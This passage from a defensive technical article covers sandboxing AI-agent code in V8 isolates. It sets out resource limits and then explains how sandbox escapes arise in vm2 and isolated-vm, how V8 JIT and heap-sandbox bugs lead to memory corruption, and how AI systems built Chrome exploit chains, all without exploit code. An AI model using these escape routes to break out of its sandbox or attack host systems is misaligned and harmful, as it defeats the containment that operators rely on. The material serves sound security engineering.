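If the company's other Workers had already used both allowances, the requests would add $0.30 and the CPU time $0.40. CPU time here includes starting the isolate and parsing the code, which Cloudflare doesn't bill for ordinary Workers.

So the loading fee is nearly the whole bill, and `cpuMs` does little to reduce it. Even if all million programs looped until the default 30-second limit, the CPU time would cost about $600, compared with at most $4 under a 200-millisecond limit. The stronger reason to set a low CPU limit is to keep one program from delaying others.

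Paid tool calls can cost far more than loading the program. If a program calls a stub that generates an image for four cents, once for each of 2,000 tickets, the calls cost $80, or 40,000 times the program's loading fee. The host function should deduct the highest possible price from a budget before each call and return any unspent amount afterwards. If it waited for the answer before deducting the price, 2,000 parallel calls could all start before anything was deducted. If several host processes serve the same customer, the balance has to be in a store they share.

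Each task also needs a limit on how many programs the model can write. Each failed program may lead the model to write another, which adds the cost of another model response and another loading fee. The limit stops an agent that keeps failing in the same way.

Cloudflare also offers an account-wide spending limit, which can reject new invocations once charges reach a threshold. It is a useful last resort, but one customer's excessive use may stop the service for all customers. The limit also doesn't cover what other companies charge for calls to their services.

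### Starting limits for a short program

The figures below suit a program that makes a few dozen to a couple of hundred calls while somebody waits for the answer. They are judgements to adjust after measuring real programs. Rivet's runtime logs a warning when use passes about 80% of a cap. These warnings help show whether a limit is catching runaway loops or restricting legitimate programs.

| Resource | Starting limit | Reason |
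|---|---|---|
| CPU time | 200 ms | Cloudflare says heavier Workers typically use 10 to 20 ms per request, so this leaves ten times as much |
| Elapsed time | 30 seconds | A person is waiting; DADL has the same default and allows up to 120 seconds for slow services |
| Each outgoing request | 10 seconds | One stalled service can't use up the whole deadline |
| Memory on Workers | 128 MB | Cloudflare fixes this, so the host should limit the size of results |
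| Memory in isolated-vm | 64 MB | An attacker who reaches three times the limit still uses less than 200 MB |
| Stub calls | 250, counted by the host | The check of 200 tickets for unpaid invoices needs 201 |
| `subRequests` | 250 | This backs up the host's count if stub calls turn out to be included |
| Calls at the same time | 6 | A parallel loop can't flood a service or use up a shared quota at once |
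| Emails and other lasting effects | 50 | One ticket search returns at most 50; a larger batch should have a person's approval |
| Programs at the same time | 4 per request | This is Cloudflare's own limit outside Durable Objects |
| Programs per task | 10 | The model has room to correct mistakes, and loading costs at most $0.02 |
| Paid calls | $1 per task | A mistaken loop costs little, and the host can ask before spending more |
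| Returned and printed text | 24,000 characters in total | This is roughly the default cut-off for results in Cloudflare's package and limits what the model has to read |

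## Escapes through the library around the isolate

Node.js developers rarely call V8 directly. A library creates the isolate or context and passes values in and out. A mistake in that library can let agent code escape even when V8 works as designed.

### vm2 and isolated-vm

Developers often confuse vm2 and isolated-vm because both packages run untrusted JavaScript inside a Node.js process. vm2 builds on the Node.js `vm` module, which runs code in a new context. Node.js's *VM (executing JavaScript)* states that the module is not a security mechanism and warns against running untrusted code in it. vm2 adds a membrane of JavaScript proxies that wrap objects passing between the host and the sandboxed code. Both sides still share a heap, so a single unwrapped host object can give the sandboxed code access to the host's `Function` and everything the Node.js process can do.

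isolated-vm gives the code its own isolate. Laverdet (2018), in *New module*, announced it at a time when, in the developer's view, the only secure way to run untrusted code in Node.js was to start a new process for it, which was cumbersome with many sandboxes. C++ code in the library copies values from one heap to the other, and the host can also hand over one of the library's `Reference` handles.

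| | vm2 | isolated-vm |
|---|---|---|
| Heap | Shared with the host | Separate |
| Barrier between code and host | Proxies written in JavaScript | V8's isolate, with C++ code that copies values across |
| Typical flaw | A host object reaches the code without a wrapper | The C++ code mishandles something the agent code controls |
| Operating-system process | The host's | The host's, unless the developer adds another |

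vm2's README lists isolated-vm among alternatives that provide "true process or hardware-level isolation". On its own, isolated-vm provides neither.

### Why host objects keep getting through

*Sanddriller* (AlHamdan and Staicu, 2023) studied the 15 vm2 breakouts known at the time and found that all of them relied on "foreign references", objects inside the sandbox that lead back to the host's built-ins. In one case, vm2 let sandboxed code call a few harmless functions of Node.js's `process` object. When one of those calls failed, it threw an exception that was a host object, and the sandboxed code received it without a wrapper.

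A membrane has to cover every way an object can arrive, including return values, exceptions and callback arguments. Even that isn't enough, because Node.js and V8 also create objects themselves. AlHamdan and Staicu traced one escape to the C++ code that Node.js uses to prepare stack traces, the lists of function calls that accompany an error. This code seemed to produce unwrapped exceptions inside the sandbox, where vm2 had no proxy to intercept them.

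The researchers reported this to the Node.js team, which replied that the sandboxes were at fault because `vm` has no security guarantee. The sandboxes' maintainers then had to restrict access to stack traces, which legitimate programs use for debugging. The researchers also worked with the Node.js team to make the documentation's warning more explicit.

Ordinary fuzzing, which feeds a program many unusual inputs and watches for crashes, tends to miss such escapes because nothing crashes. AlHamdan and Staicu's tool, SandDriller, looks for foreign references instead. It adds checks to the function calls, exception handlers and function definitions in existing test programs. Each check follows every link from a newly arrived object to see whether any leads outside the sandbox. If one does, the tool tries to change something outside, so that it reports only breaches it has demonstrated. It also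 creates up to five variants of each program, using a pattern found in nine of 27 known exploits.

The researchers started with 46,606 programs, 41,034 from the JavaScript standard's conformance tests and 5,572 from V8's own tests, and ran them against six sandboxes on three versions of Node.js. In about 17 hours, SandDriller made more than three billion checks and recorded 115,085 security violations and 48 crashes. Most were repeats, and the researchers reduced them to 13 distinct problems. The paper reports 12 confirmed flaws and eight security advisories.

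Of the six sandboxes, only ses had no violations. It freezes the built-ins so that code can't change them. But more programs failed or timed out in ses than in any other sandbox, so the test may have covered it less thoroughly.

### vm2's record

The vm2 project was once discontinued. Yarn's *vm2* page still shows the notice attached to version 3.9.19, which says that the library has critical security issues and is no longer maintained, and suggests that users consider isolated-vm. The CyberSec Guru's *Security Alert* (2026) links the decision to end maintenance to a flaw discovered in July 2023. It dates the project's revival to late 2025, and by October 2025 vm2's security page described the 3.x versions as actively maintained.

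The next serious escape, made public on 26 January 2026, involved promises, the objects that represent results still to come. vm2 sanitized the values passed to callbacks on its own promises but not on the engine's native ones. Async functions return native promises, so any sandboxed program could obtain one. Version 3.10.2 fixed the flaw, according to OSV's *CVE-2026-22709* (2026).

A larger group of flaws followed in early May. CSO Online's *13 new critical holes in JavaScript sandbox allow execution of arbitrary code* (2026) reported 13 critical flaws on 8 May, based on the maintainer's advisories. Kodem's *vm2 Sandbox Escape Vulnerabilities* (2026) also gives a total of 13, but its table includes the January flaw and so lists only 12 from May. The CyberSec Guru counts 11.

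Reports also disagree about which versions are affected. Kodem lists every version before 3.10.5 as affected by a flaw involving WebAssembly, while OSV's *CVE-2026-26956* (2026) lists only 3.10.4, and only when it runs on Node.js 25. Both give 3.10.5 as the fix. OSV's *CVE-2026-24781* (2026) gives 3.11.0 as the fix for an escape through the function that formats objects for display.

GCVE's *CVE-2026-43997* (2026) describes the shared cause most plainly. Sandboxed code could obtain the host's `Object` and use it to escape in various ways. A less severe flaw, described in OSV's *GHSA-mpf8-4hx2-7cjg* (2026), let code receive host objects through promises the host had shared. Version 3.11.0 fixed both.

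In May, CSO Online passed on the advice to install the latest version of vm2, which was then 3.11.2. Ten days later, vm2's maintainer published advisories covering all versions up to 3.11.3, with fixes in 3.11.4. In August a researcher showed that a slightly more indirect function call defeated an earlier fix, and OSV's *GHSA-cfcw-xp6x-25gj* (2026) gives 3.11.6 as the corrected version. GitLab's *Advisories for Npm/Vm2 package* lists about 45 advisories for 2026, the latest of them fixed in 3.12.1. Anyone who followed the May advice has had to update at least three more times.

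Some of the 45 only get around a time or memory limit, and others require the host to have allowed a particular Node.js module, so not all are escapes from a default installation. Allowing modules is risky because vm2 blocks dangerous ones by name and can miss some. In one of the May advisories, its list included `inspector` but omitted `inspector/promises`, through which code could still run in the host.

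Making a module read-only stops sandboxed code from altering it, but the module's functions still act with the host's authority. In one advisory in GitLab's list, code with permission to use Node.js's `https` module could use it to see credentials in the host's own requests.

vm2's long record of escapes partly reflects how many people use and study it. In October 2022, it had about 3.5 million weekly npm downloads, compared with 12,097 for isolated-vm. Even so, I wouldn't rely on a fully patched vm2 to contain agent code. Its README says that "new bypasses will likely be discovered" and strongly recommends stronger isolation for code from completely untrusted sources.

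### The isolated-vm flaw of August 2026

isolated-vm had a critical flaw of its own. It can move an `ArrayBuffer` to another isolate without copying the bytes, which saves time when the buffer is large. The caller supplies a list of the buffers to move. Staicu (2026), in *GHSA-864f-rcv7-6rh4*, explains that the library's C++ code read this list twice, once to check that every item was a buffer and again to move them. It didn't repeat the check.

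That was unsafe because the list was a live JavaScript array, which could change. In JavaScript, a property can run code each time it is read, so an item could be a real buffer during the check and something else during the move, which is a time-of-check to time-of-use error. The C++ code would then treat the other value as a buffer and follow a memory address that the attacker had influenced.

The class that does the copying appears to be available only to the host, but Staicu found that sandboxed code could reach it if the host had shared a single `Reference`. With only that `Reference`, Staicu could crash the host process, and went on to make the host call a function of the attacker's choosing, which is close to running arbitrary code in the host. Staicu gave the full exploit only to the maintainer.

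The sandboxed program made isolated-vm's C++ code, which can access both heaps, misuse memory. V8's own separation between the heaps remained intact, so users had to update isolated-vm itself; updating Node.js would not have fixed the flaw. It affects version 7.0.0 and every version before 6.2.0, and is fixed in 6.2.0 and 7.0.1. Endor Labs' *GHSA-864f-rcv7-6rh4* entry rates its severity 10 out of 10.

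The fix prevents any JavaScript from running while the library makes a copy, so an item in the list cannot change during copying. A second type check would also have closed this gap, but the same mistake elsewhere in the copying code could have opened another.

The flaw had no CVE number when SecurityWeek covered it. Many security tools track flaws by CVE number, so a team that searched only for those numbers could have missed it. Checking the installed version is safer.

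Staicu names several products that run users' or models' code with isolated-vm, including Mastra's code mode, the automation platforms Activepieces and Sim.ai, the low-code platform Budibase, the data platform Directus and the chat server Rocket.Chat. The automation platform n8n recommends the library for isolating its users' scripts. isolated-vm's documentation also lists Screeps, a game that runs players' code, along with Fly.io, Algolia and Tripadvisor. Staicu doesn't report an attack on any of them. Whether an installation was vulnerable depended on its version and on whether untrusted code could obtain a `Reference`.

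Staicu describes sharing a `Reference` as the standard way to give a sandbox any capability, but the maintainers tell developers never to let untrusted code have one. A host can share a capability without exposing the `Reference` by running its own setup code in the isolate before the agent's program. The setup code keeps the `Reference` in a private variable and gives the program only an ordinary function that uses it. That function needs careful review because it runs in the same isolate as the agent's code.

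Earlier flaws also support the maintainers' warning. In 2021, AlHamdan and Staicu reported that code with a `Reference` could follow its links to the host's `Function`. The maintainers first replied that users knew about the danger, but they changed the library after seeing several vulnerable applications. OSV's *CVE-2021-21413* (2021) lists 4.0.0 as the fixed version.

Another flaw let an attacker escape the sandbox by supplying cached data, which V8 saves so that it can load a script faster next time. Version 4.3.7 added a warning to the documentation, according to OSV's *CVE-2022-39266* (2022), so installing that version doesn't protect a host that still accepts cached data from users.

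Haynes points out in Endor Labs' companion to Staicu's article that Chrome separates tabs mostly by process and that isolated-vm adds no process of its own. Staicu's article needs correction where it says that Chrome uses isolates to separate tabs and that the operating system helps enforce isolated-vm's boundary. An attacker who exploited a similar bug in Chrome would still be confined to one of the browser's processes, but in a typical isolated-vm installation the attacker would already be in the process that holds the application's data and keys.

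### Native code behind the stubs

Flaws of this kind are common in native extensions, the C or C++ parts of packages for languages such as JavaScript. Staicu, Rahaman and colleagues (2021), in *Bilingual Problems*, looked for extensions that convert a JavaScript value to a C++ type without first checking what it is. They collected 6,432 npm packages with native code in February 2021 and used a program to trace how each one handled its arguments.

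The analysis found 1,669 packages in which an argument flowed into a type conversion. The native code checked the type in 939 of them but not in the other 730. Some of the 730 check it earlier, in JavaScript, so the researchers examined the riskiest conversions by hand. They built working exploits for 33 packages. The exploits crashed Node.js, exposed leftover memory or leaked memory until the machine slowed down. The researchers also searched 1,993 projects that used seven of the vulnerable packages and found six web applications that an outsider could crash over the internet. The work led to seven CVEs, six rated high severity.

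The researchers blame Node.js's permissive design for most of these bugs. When a value has the wrong type, Python and Ruby raise an exception. One of the two Node.js interfaces they studied returns an error code that the developer may ignore, and the other doesn't detect the mismatch. The Node.js team considered these to be faults in the packages but promised to fix some of the behaviour.

The attackers in this study could do less than agent code can. They couldn't run programs and could send only JSON-compatible data, which is also what a typical code-mode stub accepts. Suppose the support agent's host accesses its ticket database through an old version of `sqlite3`, one of the packages the researchers crashed. If a stub forwards the program's arguments unchecked, the program could send a certain kind of object in place of a string and crash the whole host. A `try` block in the host wouldn't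 catch the crash, because it happens in native code. A run-time check like the one in `getCustomer` would reject the object before it reached the database package.

### Checks for anyone writing a binding

A binding, the code that connects the isolate to the host, should copy each incoming value, then check and use only the copy. Passing arguments as JSON text provides most of this protection automatically, because parsing produces plain data that can't run code or change between reads. The host doesn't get this protection if it accepts live objects from agent code, since such an object may return a different value each time the host uses it.

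The same error can occur without C++. If an employee approved an email and the host then read its text from the program again, the program could return a different message.

No agent code should run while the binding makes its copy. This is easy to get wrong in JavaScript, because reading a property, converting an object to a string or iterating over an array can all call functions that the agent's program defined. In C++, the developer can have V8 forbid JavaScript during the copy, as the isolated-vm fix does, so enforcing the rule doesn't depend on a reviewer finding every place where agent code could run. After a flaw in May, vm2's maintainer wrote a similar rule that the membrane's internal containers must not invoke sandboxed code, but GitLab's list includes a later advisory about another part of vm2 that broke the rule in the same way.

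The binding should also expose as few objects as possible. Exposing an object also exposes its constructor and everything linked to it, which the developer may not realize. For most stubs, a plain function that takes and returns copied data is enough.

The boundary needs its own fuzz tests. These can use lists that change length while the host reads them, properties that return a new value each time, and functions that throw exceptions at unexpected points. *Empirical Security Analysis of Software-based Fault Isolation through Controlled Fault Injection* (2025) describes a similar tool, which alters untrusted data just as trusted code reads it. The tool found 19 security bugs in the V8 heap sandbox, a defence inside the engine.

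Tests should look for crashes and also check, as SandDriller does, whether any object inside the sandbox leads back to the host. They are worth repeating on every version of Node.js the product supports, because AlHamdan and Staicu found escapes that worked only on some versions. Several of vm2's 2026 flaws appear only on Node.js 25 or 26, so updating Node.js to get V8's security fixes can expose a new flaw in vm2.

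## Escapes through bugs in V8 itself

The isolated-vm flaw of August 2026 left V8's own separation between heaps intact. A flaw in V8 itself can break that separation. Narrow stubs and careful bindings then no longer help, because the agent code can change memory without calling them.

### How a wrong assumption becomes a memory bug

A JavaScript variable can hold a number and later a string. Checking the type of every value before every operation would be slow, so V8 starts each program in an interpreter and records which types each function handles. When a function has run often enough, a just-in-time (JIT) compiler turns it into machine code specialised for those types.

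Suppose the support agent's program adds up thousands of invoice amounts, and every amount so far has been a small whole number. The compiled code does little more than check that each amount is a whole number and add it to the total. If an amount is a string, the check fails and V8 returns to slower code that can handle any type, so the program still gets the right answer.

Each check takes time, so the compiler removes those that seem redundant, such as a second check on a value that nothing could have changed since the first. Many engine bugs occur because the compiler wrongly treats a value as unchanged.

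The V8 developers illustrate this with an invented array function that reads an item, converts it to a number and writes a result back to the same position. JavaScript lets an object define its own conversion to a number, and that conversion can run code that shortens the array. If the function doesn't check the position again because it has already read from it, the write can land beyond the array's new end. A programmer can make this mistake when writing a function by hand, as can a compiler when it chooses which checks to drop.

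Reading or writing past the end of an object is called an out-of-bounds access. In type confusion, the other common failure, machine code treats a value of one type as if it were another. Here is a simplified picture of both:

```
Memory:         | slot 0 | slot 1 | slot 2 | next object: a buffer's length |

Type confusion: slot 1 holds a reference to a customer record.
                The machine code treats it as a whole number.

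Out of bounds:  the array ends at slot 2.
                The machine code writes to "slot 3" and so
                changes the length of the buffer next door.
```

Either error can be enough to take over the heap. For example, once the buffer's recorded length is wrong, ordinary JavaScript can use the buffer to read and write memory past its end.

Rewriting V8 in Rust, a language whose compiler rejects most memory errors, would solve only part of the problem. Rust would probably catch the mistake in the hand-written function, but not the same mistake in a JIT compiler, because the compiler itself would run safely and only the machine code it produced would be faulty. Switching off the JIT compilers would also be only a partial fix. The V8 developers say that roughly half of the exploited V8 bugs were in a compiler, and the rest were in parts such as the interpreter, the parser and the garbage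 collector. Doing both would make heavy computation 1.5 to 10 times slower, or worse.

Running V8 without its optimising compilers slows code down, which matters more to a browser than to a tool-calling program that may use 10 milliseconds of processor time and then wait seconds for replies. A host that controls its own copy of V8 can turn these compilers off, and for such programs I think the added security is usually worth the lost speed. A tight CPU limit isn't a substitute, because a hostile loop can trigger compilation within milliseconds.

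### What 241 engine flaws have in common

Ma, Hu and colleagues (2026), in *When Flaws Cascade*, gathered 1,215 publicly reported flaws in four engines: V8, Safari's JavaScriptCore, Firefox's SpiderMonkey and ChakraCore, which older versions of Microsoft Edge used. They kept 241 well-documented flaws from 2017 to 2024 that had a severity score above 7 out of 10 or had earned a bounty, and 93 of these were in V8. Three security researchers labelled each flaw's symptom and cause, and a more senior colleague settled disagreements.

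| Root cause | Share of the 241 flaws |
|---|---|
| Incorrect handling of types | 31.5% |
| Incorrect handling of data structures, such as a missing bounds check | 29.5% |
| Errors in an optimisation algorithm | 18.7% |
| Mismanaged memory and other resources | 11.6% |
| Incorrect control flow | 3.3% |
| Other | 5.4% |

ChakraCore accounts for half of the type errors. In V8, data structures are the most common cause, at 38.7%.

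Of the 93 V8 flaws, 44 showed up directly as memory errors. These were 25 out-of-bounds accesses, 15 type confusions and four use-after-free errors, in which code keeps using memory the engine has already released. Another 19 caused one of V8's internal consistency checks to fail, and the remaining 30 only made a program behave incorrectly.

Wrong behaviour can lead to a memory error. Across all four engines, the researchers replayed the 75 flaws that came with a working demonstration. Of these, 32 corrupted memory at once, and the other 43 did so through a series of steps. In one flaw from 2020, an optimisation that avoids repeating identical calculations produced a wrong number, from which the compiler inferred the wrong range for an array index. That range seemed to fit inside the array, so the compiler removed the bounds check, and the program could read outside the array.

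In 30 of the 43 cases, the compiler removed a protection the program needed. It dropped bounds checks in 16 cases, type checks in 12, and in two the bookkeeping the garbage collector uses to identify objects still in use. JIT compilation played a part in 39 of the 43. With the 32 direct cases added to the total, that is 39 of 75, or 52%, which is close to the V8 developers' "roughly half".

These proportions come from flaws that somebody thought worth documenting in detail, so they may overstate the share of elaborate compiler bugs. They are still a good guide to what attackers look for.

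Fixing one flaw often leaves the remaining steps of an exploit usable. In November 2018, V8's developers corrected an error in the compiler's range estimates that had led it to remove bounds checks. Another flaw then led to the same removal. In February 2019, the developers made it harder for a wrong range to remove the checks, but by November a new flaw had bypassed this protection through the way V8 computed an array's length.

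### The V8 heap sandbox

V8's developers therefore also try to limit the damage a bug can do. Nearly all the V8 bugs that attackers exploit initially corrupt memory inside the JavaScript heap. Objects there used to contain raw 64-bit addresses, so an attacker who overwrote an address could make V8 read or write anywhere in the process's memory. The V8 heap sandbox removes those addresses from the heap.

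When it starts, V8 reserves a range of addresses one tebibyte (TiB) long. This uses up addresses but hardly any physical memory. Everything that a typical V8 bug can corrupt goes inside the range, and V8 replaces the raw addresses in four ways:

- A reference from one JavaScript object to another becomes a 32-bit offset from the start of the range. The objects occupy the first 4 gibibytes (GiB), which is as far as 32 bits can count.
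- The contents of an `ArrayBuffer` can lie anywhere in the range, so a reference to them is a 40-bit offset.
- For something outside the range, such as one of the host's C++ objects, the JavaScript object holds only an index into a table. The table is outside the range too, and holds the real address.
- Objects that V8 has to trust, including its bytecode (the instructions its interpreter runs) and the records that describe compiled code, live outside the range. JavaScript objects refer to them through another table.

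An example shows why a corrupted offset stays inside. Suppose the range starts at address `0x530000000000` and a ticket refers to a customer record. Leaving out a marker bit that V8 keeps in each reference, the calculation is:

```
start of the range              0x530000000000
+ offset stored in the ticket   0x000000041a28
= address of the record         0x530000041a28
```

An attacker who can overwrite the offset may choose any 32-bit number. The largest gives:

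```
start of the range              0x530000000000
+ largest 32-bit offset         0x0000ffffffff
= highest address within reach  0x5300ffffffff
```

The largest value a compressed pointer can hold refers to the last byte of the 4 GiB set aside for objects. The pointer doesn't store the start of that range, so an attacker can't change the start by overwriting the pointer.

Buffers work similarly. The field that holds a buffer's offset is 64 bits wide, but V8 shifts the value right by 24 bits before using it, so the offset is at most 40 bits long whatever the attacker writes. The highest address at which a buffer can start is therefore `0x53ffffffffff`, the last byte of the 1 TiB range. If the host keeps an access token at `0x7f1200000000`, reaching it would take a 46-bit offset. A long buffer that starts near the end of the range could still extend past it, so V8 limits the size of buffers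 and leaves unusable addresses on either side of the range, where any access crashes the process.

The tables work like the numbered file handles that an operating system gives a program. An attacker can swap one index for another but can't write a new address into the table.

The heap sandbox slowed typical workloads by about 1% or less when V8's developers measured it, around the time Google added it to Chrome's bug-bounty programme (about version 123 of the browser). It works only on 64-bit systems. It is on by default where V8 supports it, but developers can turn it off when they compile V8, so anyone who runs agent code on a V8-based server should check how that copy was built.

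### What the heap sandbox promises

The threat model in Chromium's *V8 Sandbox* README assumes that an attacker can change any memory inside the sandbox at any time, even while V8 is using it, and can read memory outside the sandbox, for example through hardware side channels. The sandbox tries to stop the attacker from corrupting memory outside it.

Some writes outside the sandbox don't count as failures, because V8 may trap the write in a safe region or recheck a counter before relying on it. Tricking the garbage collector into freeing objects also doesn't count, provided the collector's own records stay consistent and the damage stays within the sandbox's address range.

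This leaves two gaps for tenants who share a process. The first is that the heap sandbox's guarantee covers only writes outside its range, and an attacker can steal an access token just by reading it. If the host keeps the mail service's token in memory outside that range, the sandbox isn't guaranteed to keep it secret.

The other gap is within the sandbox's address range, because isolates in one process share a heap sandbox unless the host arranges otherwise. An attacker who can corrupt the whole range can read and change the heaps of neighbouring isolates, which may hold another company's tickets. Under the threat model, this is not a breach of the sandbox. The host's own JavaScript is also exposed if its isolate uses the same range. Cloudflare limits this exposure by dividing isolates among several heap sandboxes and adding hardware memory keys.

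The heap sandbox makes it harder to turn a V8 bug into control of the process, but it was not designed to keep tenants' data apart.

### Looking for ways out of the heap sandbox

A bypass usually depends on trusted code that reads a number from inside the sandbox's memory range and relies on it. The V8 developers give an example in which C++ code lists the names of an object's properties. The code reads the total number of properties and creates a list of that size outside the range. It then fills the list using a second number, the count of properties stored directly in the object, which should be no larger than the total. An attacker can change both numbers, and raising the second makes the code write past the end of the list unless an explicit bounds check prevents it.

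Ordinary fuzzing is poorly suited to finding these errors, because it starts with an intact heap. *Empirical Security Analysis of Software-based Fault Isolation through Controlled Fault Injection* starts where the threat model does, with an attacker who already controls everything in the range. Its tool, SbxBrk, works in four steps:

1. While compiling V8, it adds a check before each instruction that might read from the range. Analysing the code beforehand rules out nearly half of the 1.4 million candidates.
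2. It runs test programs. When V8 reads a value from the range, the tool may first flip some of its bits and store the altered value back in memory. Most of the changes are small, since V8's existing checks tend to reject large ones.
3. If a change takes V8 into code that no earlier test had reached, the tool keeps that change and builds on it.
4. It reports a bug when V8 corrupts memory outside the range. It ignores outside reads, in line with the threat model.

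For comparison, the researchers extended Fuzzilli, Google's fuzzer for JavaScript engines, to call a V8 testing interface that overwrites memory in the range. They ran each tool ten times for three days, with 384 copies working in parallel, on a version of V8 from December 2024. SbxBrk found six security bugs, and the extended Fuzzilli found one of those six. The result shows that general fuzzing misses many of these bugs, but it is a weaker measure of how well a fuzzer could do, because the researchers describe their extension as unsophisticated.

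SbxBrk found no security bugs when it stopped using code coverage to choose which changes to keep. It also found none when it altered values during V8's start-up, because these early changes often stopped V8 from reaching the first line of the test program. V8 reads from the range 193,639 times before that point.

With further runs, the total came to 19. Google fixed 17 and marked the other two as duplicates. They include several recurring kinds of error:

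- **Reading a value twice.** A function that sorts arrays of numbers read the array's size once to set aside memory and again to do the sorting. An attacker who changed the size in between could make it sort more memory than it had set aside. The cause is the same as in the isolated-vm flaw.
- **Impossible values.** V8 stores some choices as small numbers, each with a defined meaning. Code outside the range had no branch for a number with no meaning, and its behaviour then became undefined. After the researchers reported several cases, V8's developers opened a general task to harden this kind of code.
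- **Impossible lengths.** Several functions that process text overflowed when a string's recorded length was far greater than any real string's.

One bug appeared only when the researchers compiled V8 without optimisation. The source code stored an index in the range and then used it. An optimised build would probably keep the index in the processor, out of the attacker's reach, but the unoptimised build read it back from memory. The researchers also compared two versions of a C++ compiler released six months apart, and found that 2.84% of the source lines that read memory produced a different number of reads. A line of V8 code that is safe in one build may therefore be unsafe in the next, even if nobody has edited it.

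These findings partly support the V8 developers' argument for the heap sandbox. The developers hoped the sandbox would become easier to defend than V8 itself, since most bypasses come from simple mistakes that bounds checks or a memory-safe language can prevent. Most of the 19 bugs are of that sort. But the code that has to be correct includes every built-in function in the JavaScript standard, and it changes constantly.

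### The flaws attackers used in 2026

Kovacs (2026) reported in *Chrome Update Patches Exploited XML Zero-Day, Eighth This Year* that by 9 November 2026, Google had fixed eight Chrome flaws that attackers were already exploiting. Google fixed the same number in all of 2025, according to IBTimes Australia's *Google Patches Eighth Actively Exploited Chrome Zero-Day of 2026* (2026). An update on 1 December fixed 229 more flaws, with no report that attackers were using any of them, according to PCQuest's *Chrome patches 229 security flaws* (2026).

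At least three of the eight were in V8:

| Flaw | Google's fix | Class |
|---|---|---|
| CVE-2026-11645 | June | Out-of-bounds read and write |
| CVE-2026-85046 | September | Type confusion |
| CVE-2026-87491 | September | Out-of-bounds write |

The eighth was in code that processes XML. It can't affect a server that runs V8 without the rest of the browser, so the total for Chrome overstates the danger to such a server.

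Google has published little about the causes. The clearest account is from Salvatore Gulizia, who reported CVE-2026-85046. Help Net Security's *Google patches actively exploited Chrome zero-day (CVE-2026-85046)* (2026) quotes his explanation. V8 internally labels each array by the kind of items it holds. A bug in the compilers gave an array that could hold any kind of object the label for arrays of small whole numbers. Code that relied on the label then treated object references as numbers. Gulizia writes that an attacker could use this to read and write anywhere on the JavaScript heap.

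Gulizia reported the flaw on 4 August and received $1,000. Two days later Jihyeon Jeong, of Seoul National University, reported CVE-2026-87491, for which Google paid $2,500. Google rated the second flaw only "Medium" in severity, even though attackers were using it (Help Net Security, *Google fixes yet another actively exploited Chrome zero-day (CVE-2026-87491)*, 2026).

### Bugs found by AI systems

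Attackers are known to have used only a handful of V8 flaws in 2026, but automated tools found many more. Groß (2026), in *Fuzzers vs. AI*, compared two tools that Google runs on V8 continuously. Fuzzilli generates JavaScript programs and watches for crashes. Big Sleep is an AI agent that reads each day's changes to V8's source code and writes a test program for any bug it finds. The comparison covers April to September 2026:

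| Reports | Big Sleep | Fuzzilli |
|---|---|---|
| All bugs | 441 | 316 |
| Labelled as vulnerabilities | 95 | 178 |
| Vulnerabilities with a fix, leaving out duplicates and intended behaviour | 45 | 37 |

The last row is the fairest comparison because many of Fuzzilli's reports were of the same bug causing slightly different crashes, and many of Big Sleep's early reports were of configuration problems with little effect on security.

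Fuzzing and AI found partly different vulnerabilities. In the bug tracker, about 25% of them overlapped. That method tends to miss matches, so Groß also ran experiments on vulnerabilities reported since 2023 and found an overlap of roughly 60%. On either figure, replacing fuzzing with AI would miss a substantial share of the bugs. Groß doesn't compare costs because Google hasn't tuned either system for cost.

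Big Sleep's 45 vulnerabilities amount to about one every four days. But both tools concentrate on newly added code, so Google may have fixed many of these before they reached a stable release. The number is a better indication of how easily V8's developers introduce such bugs than of how many remain unfixed in a current version.

The same trend extends to the rest of Chrome. Google's *Stronger with every update* (2026) reports 1,072 security fixes in versions 149 and 150, more than in the previous 23 versions combined. By March 2026, Google had received more bug reports that year than in all of 2025. The additional fixes help only those who install them promptly.

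AI systems can also turn bugs into working attacks. In Anthropic's *Discovering and exploiting vulnerabilities in critical, real-world software with Claude* (2026), the company describes how an unreleased research model built an attack on Chrome that needs a user only to open a web page. Mynavi News' *Anthropicの未公開AI、複数の脆弱性を組み合わせた攻撃コードを開発* (2026) outlines its four stages:

| Stage | Kind of flaw | What the attacker gained |
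|---|---|---|
| 1 | Memory corruption in V8 | Control of memory in the JavaScript heap |
| 2 | A bypass of the V8 heap sandbox | Control of the process that displays the page |
| 3 | A race condition in the browser's cache storage | Knowledge of the main browser process's memory layout |
| 4 | A use-after-free error in a login feature | The ability to run code outside Chrome's process sandbox |

The attack was part of a larger search. Google assigned 62 CVE numbers to the Chrome flaws Anthropic reported, and had fixed them all by version 156. According to Kumari's *Unreleased Claude model found attack chains in Chrome, Safari*, 21 of the flaws could compromise the process that displays a page, and 13 could help an attacker escape a sandbox.

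The security company XBOW also used AI agents to build a complete attack on Chrome. The attack combined a V8 compiler bug with a bug in an image decoder and another in Chrome's crash reporter. Dolan-Gavitt (2026) says in *Zero to Calc in Six Days* that the work took six days in August, whereas a team of four would once have needed six to nine months. XBOW's first attempt took two months. Google paid $250,000 for the result.

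Engine attacks used to take rare skill and months of work, so an operator running agent code could reasonably assume that nobody would use one against a small service. That assumption is weaker now because far more people could mount an attack with six days of work by AI agents, though this may still be expensive.

### What "inside the sandbox" means on a server

According to Chrome's advisories, an attacker could use either of the two V8 flaws fixed in September to run code "inside the sandbox". This phrase normally refers to Chrome's process sandbox, the operating-system restrictions on the process that displays a page, so it is not evidence that the V8 heap sandbox held.

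In Chrome, an attacker who gets that far is still quite confined. Arni Hardarson, one of the people who reported the XML flaw, says in Information Age's *Melbourne researcher discovers Chrome bug in 27yo code* that such an attacker might read or change data available to that process, but would generally need another flaw to install malware. That barrier is probably one reason Google can rate an exploited V8 flaw as "Medium".

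On a server, as with isolated-vm, the process that contains V8 is often the host itself, so without an outer layer code "inside the sandbox" has the host's files, network access and tokens. What stands in the way after the first V8 bug depends on the installation:

| Where V8 runs | Barriers left after an attacker corrupts the JavaScript heap |
|---|---|
| A Chrome tab | The V8 heap sandbox, then the process sandbox |
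| A server with the heap sandbox but no outer layer | The V8 heap sandbox |
| A server with neither | None |

An attack like Anthropic's would need only its first two stages on the second kind of server, and only the first stage on the third kind. An attacker would have to adapt the details, since a server lacks many of the browser's features. But the attacker wouldn't have to persuade anyone to visit a web page, because the host runs agent code on request.

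The same effect occurs in desktop applications. Cyber Security News describes an experiment in which a researcher used Claude Opus to attack the chat program Discord, which contained an outdated copy of Chrome's engine, version 138. Discord ran its main window without a process sandbox, so the researcher needed only two flaws to escape instead of three.

Chrome's severity ratings therefore don't apply to a server. Without an outer layer, "inside the sandbox" means in the host process, so the operator should treat a V8 flaw described that way as critical, whatever Google's rating.

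## Reading another tenant's memory through timing

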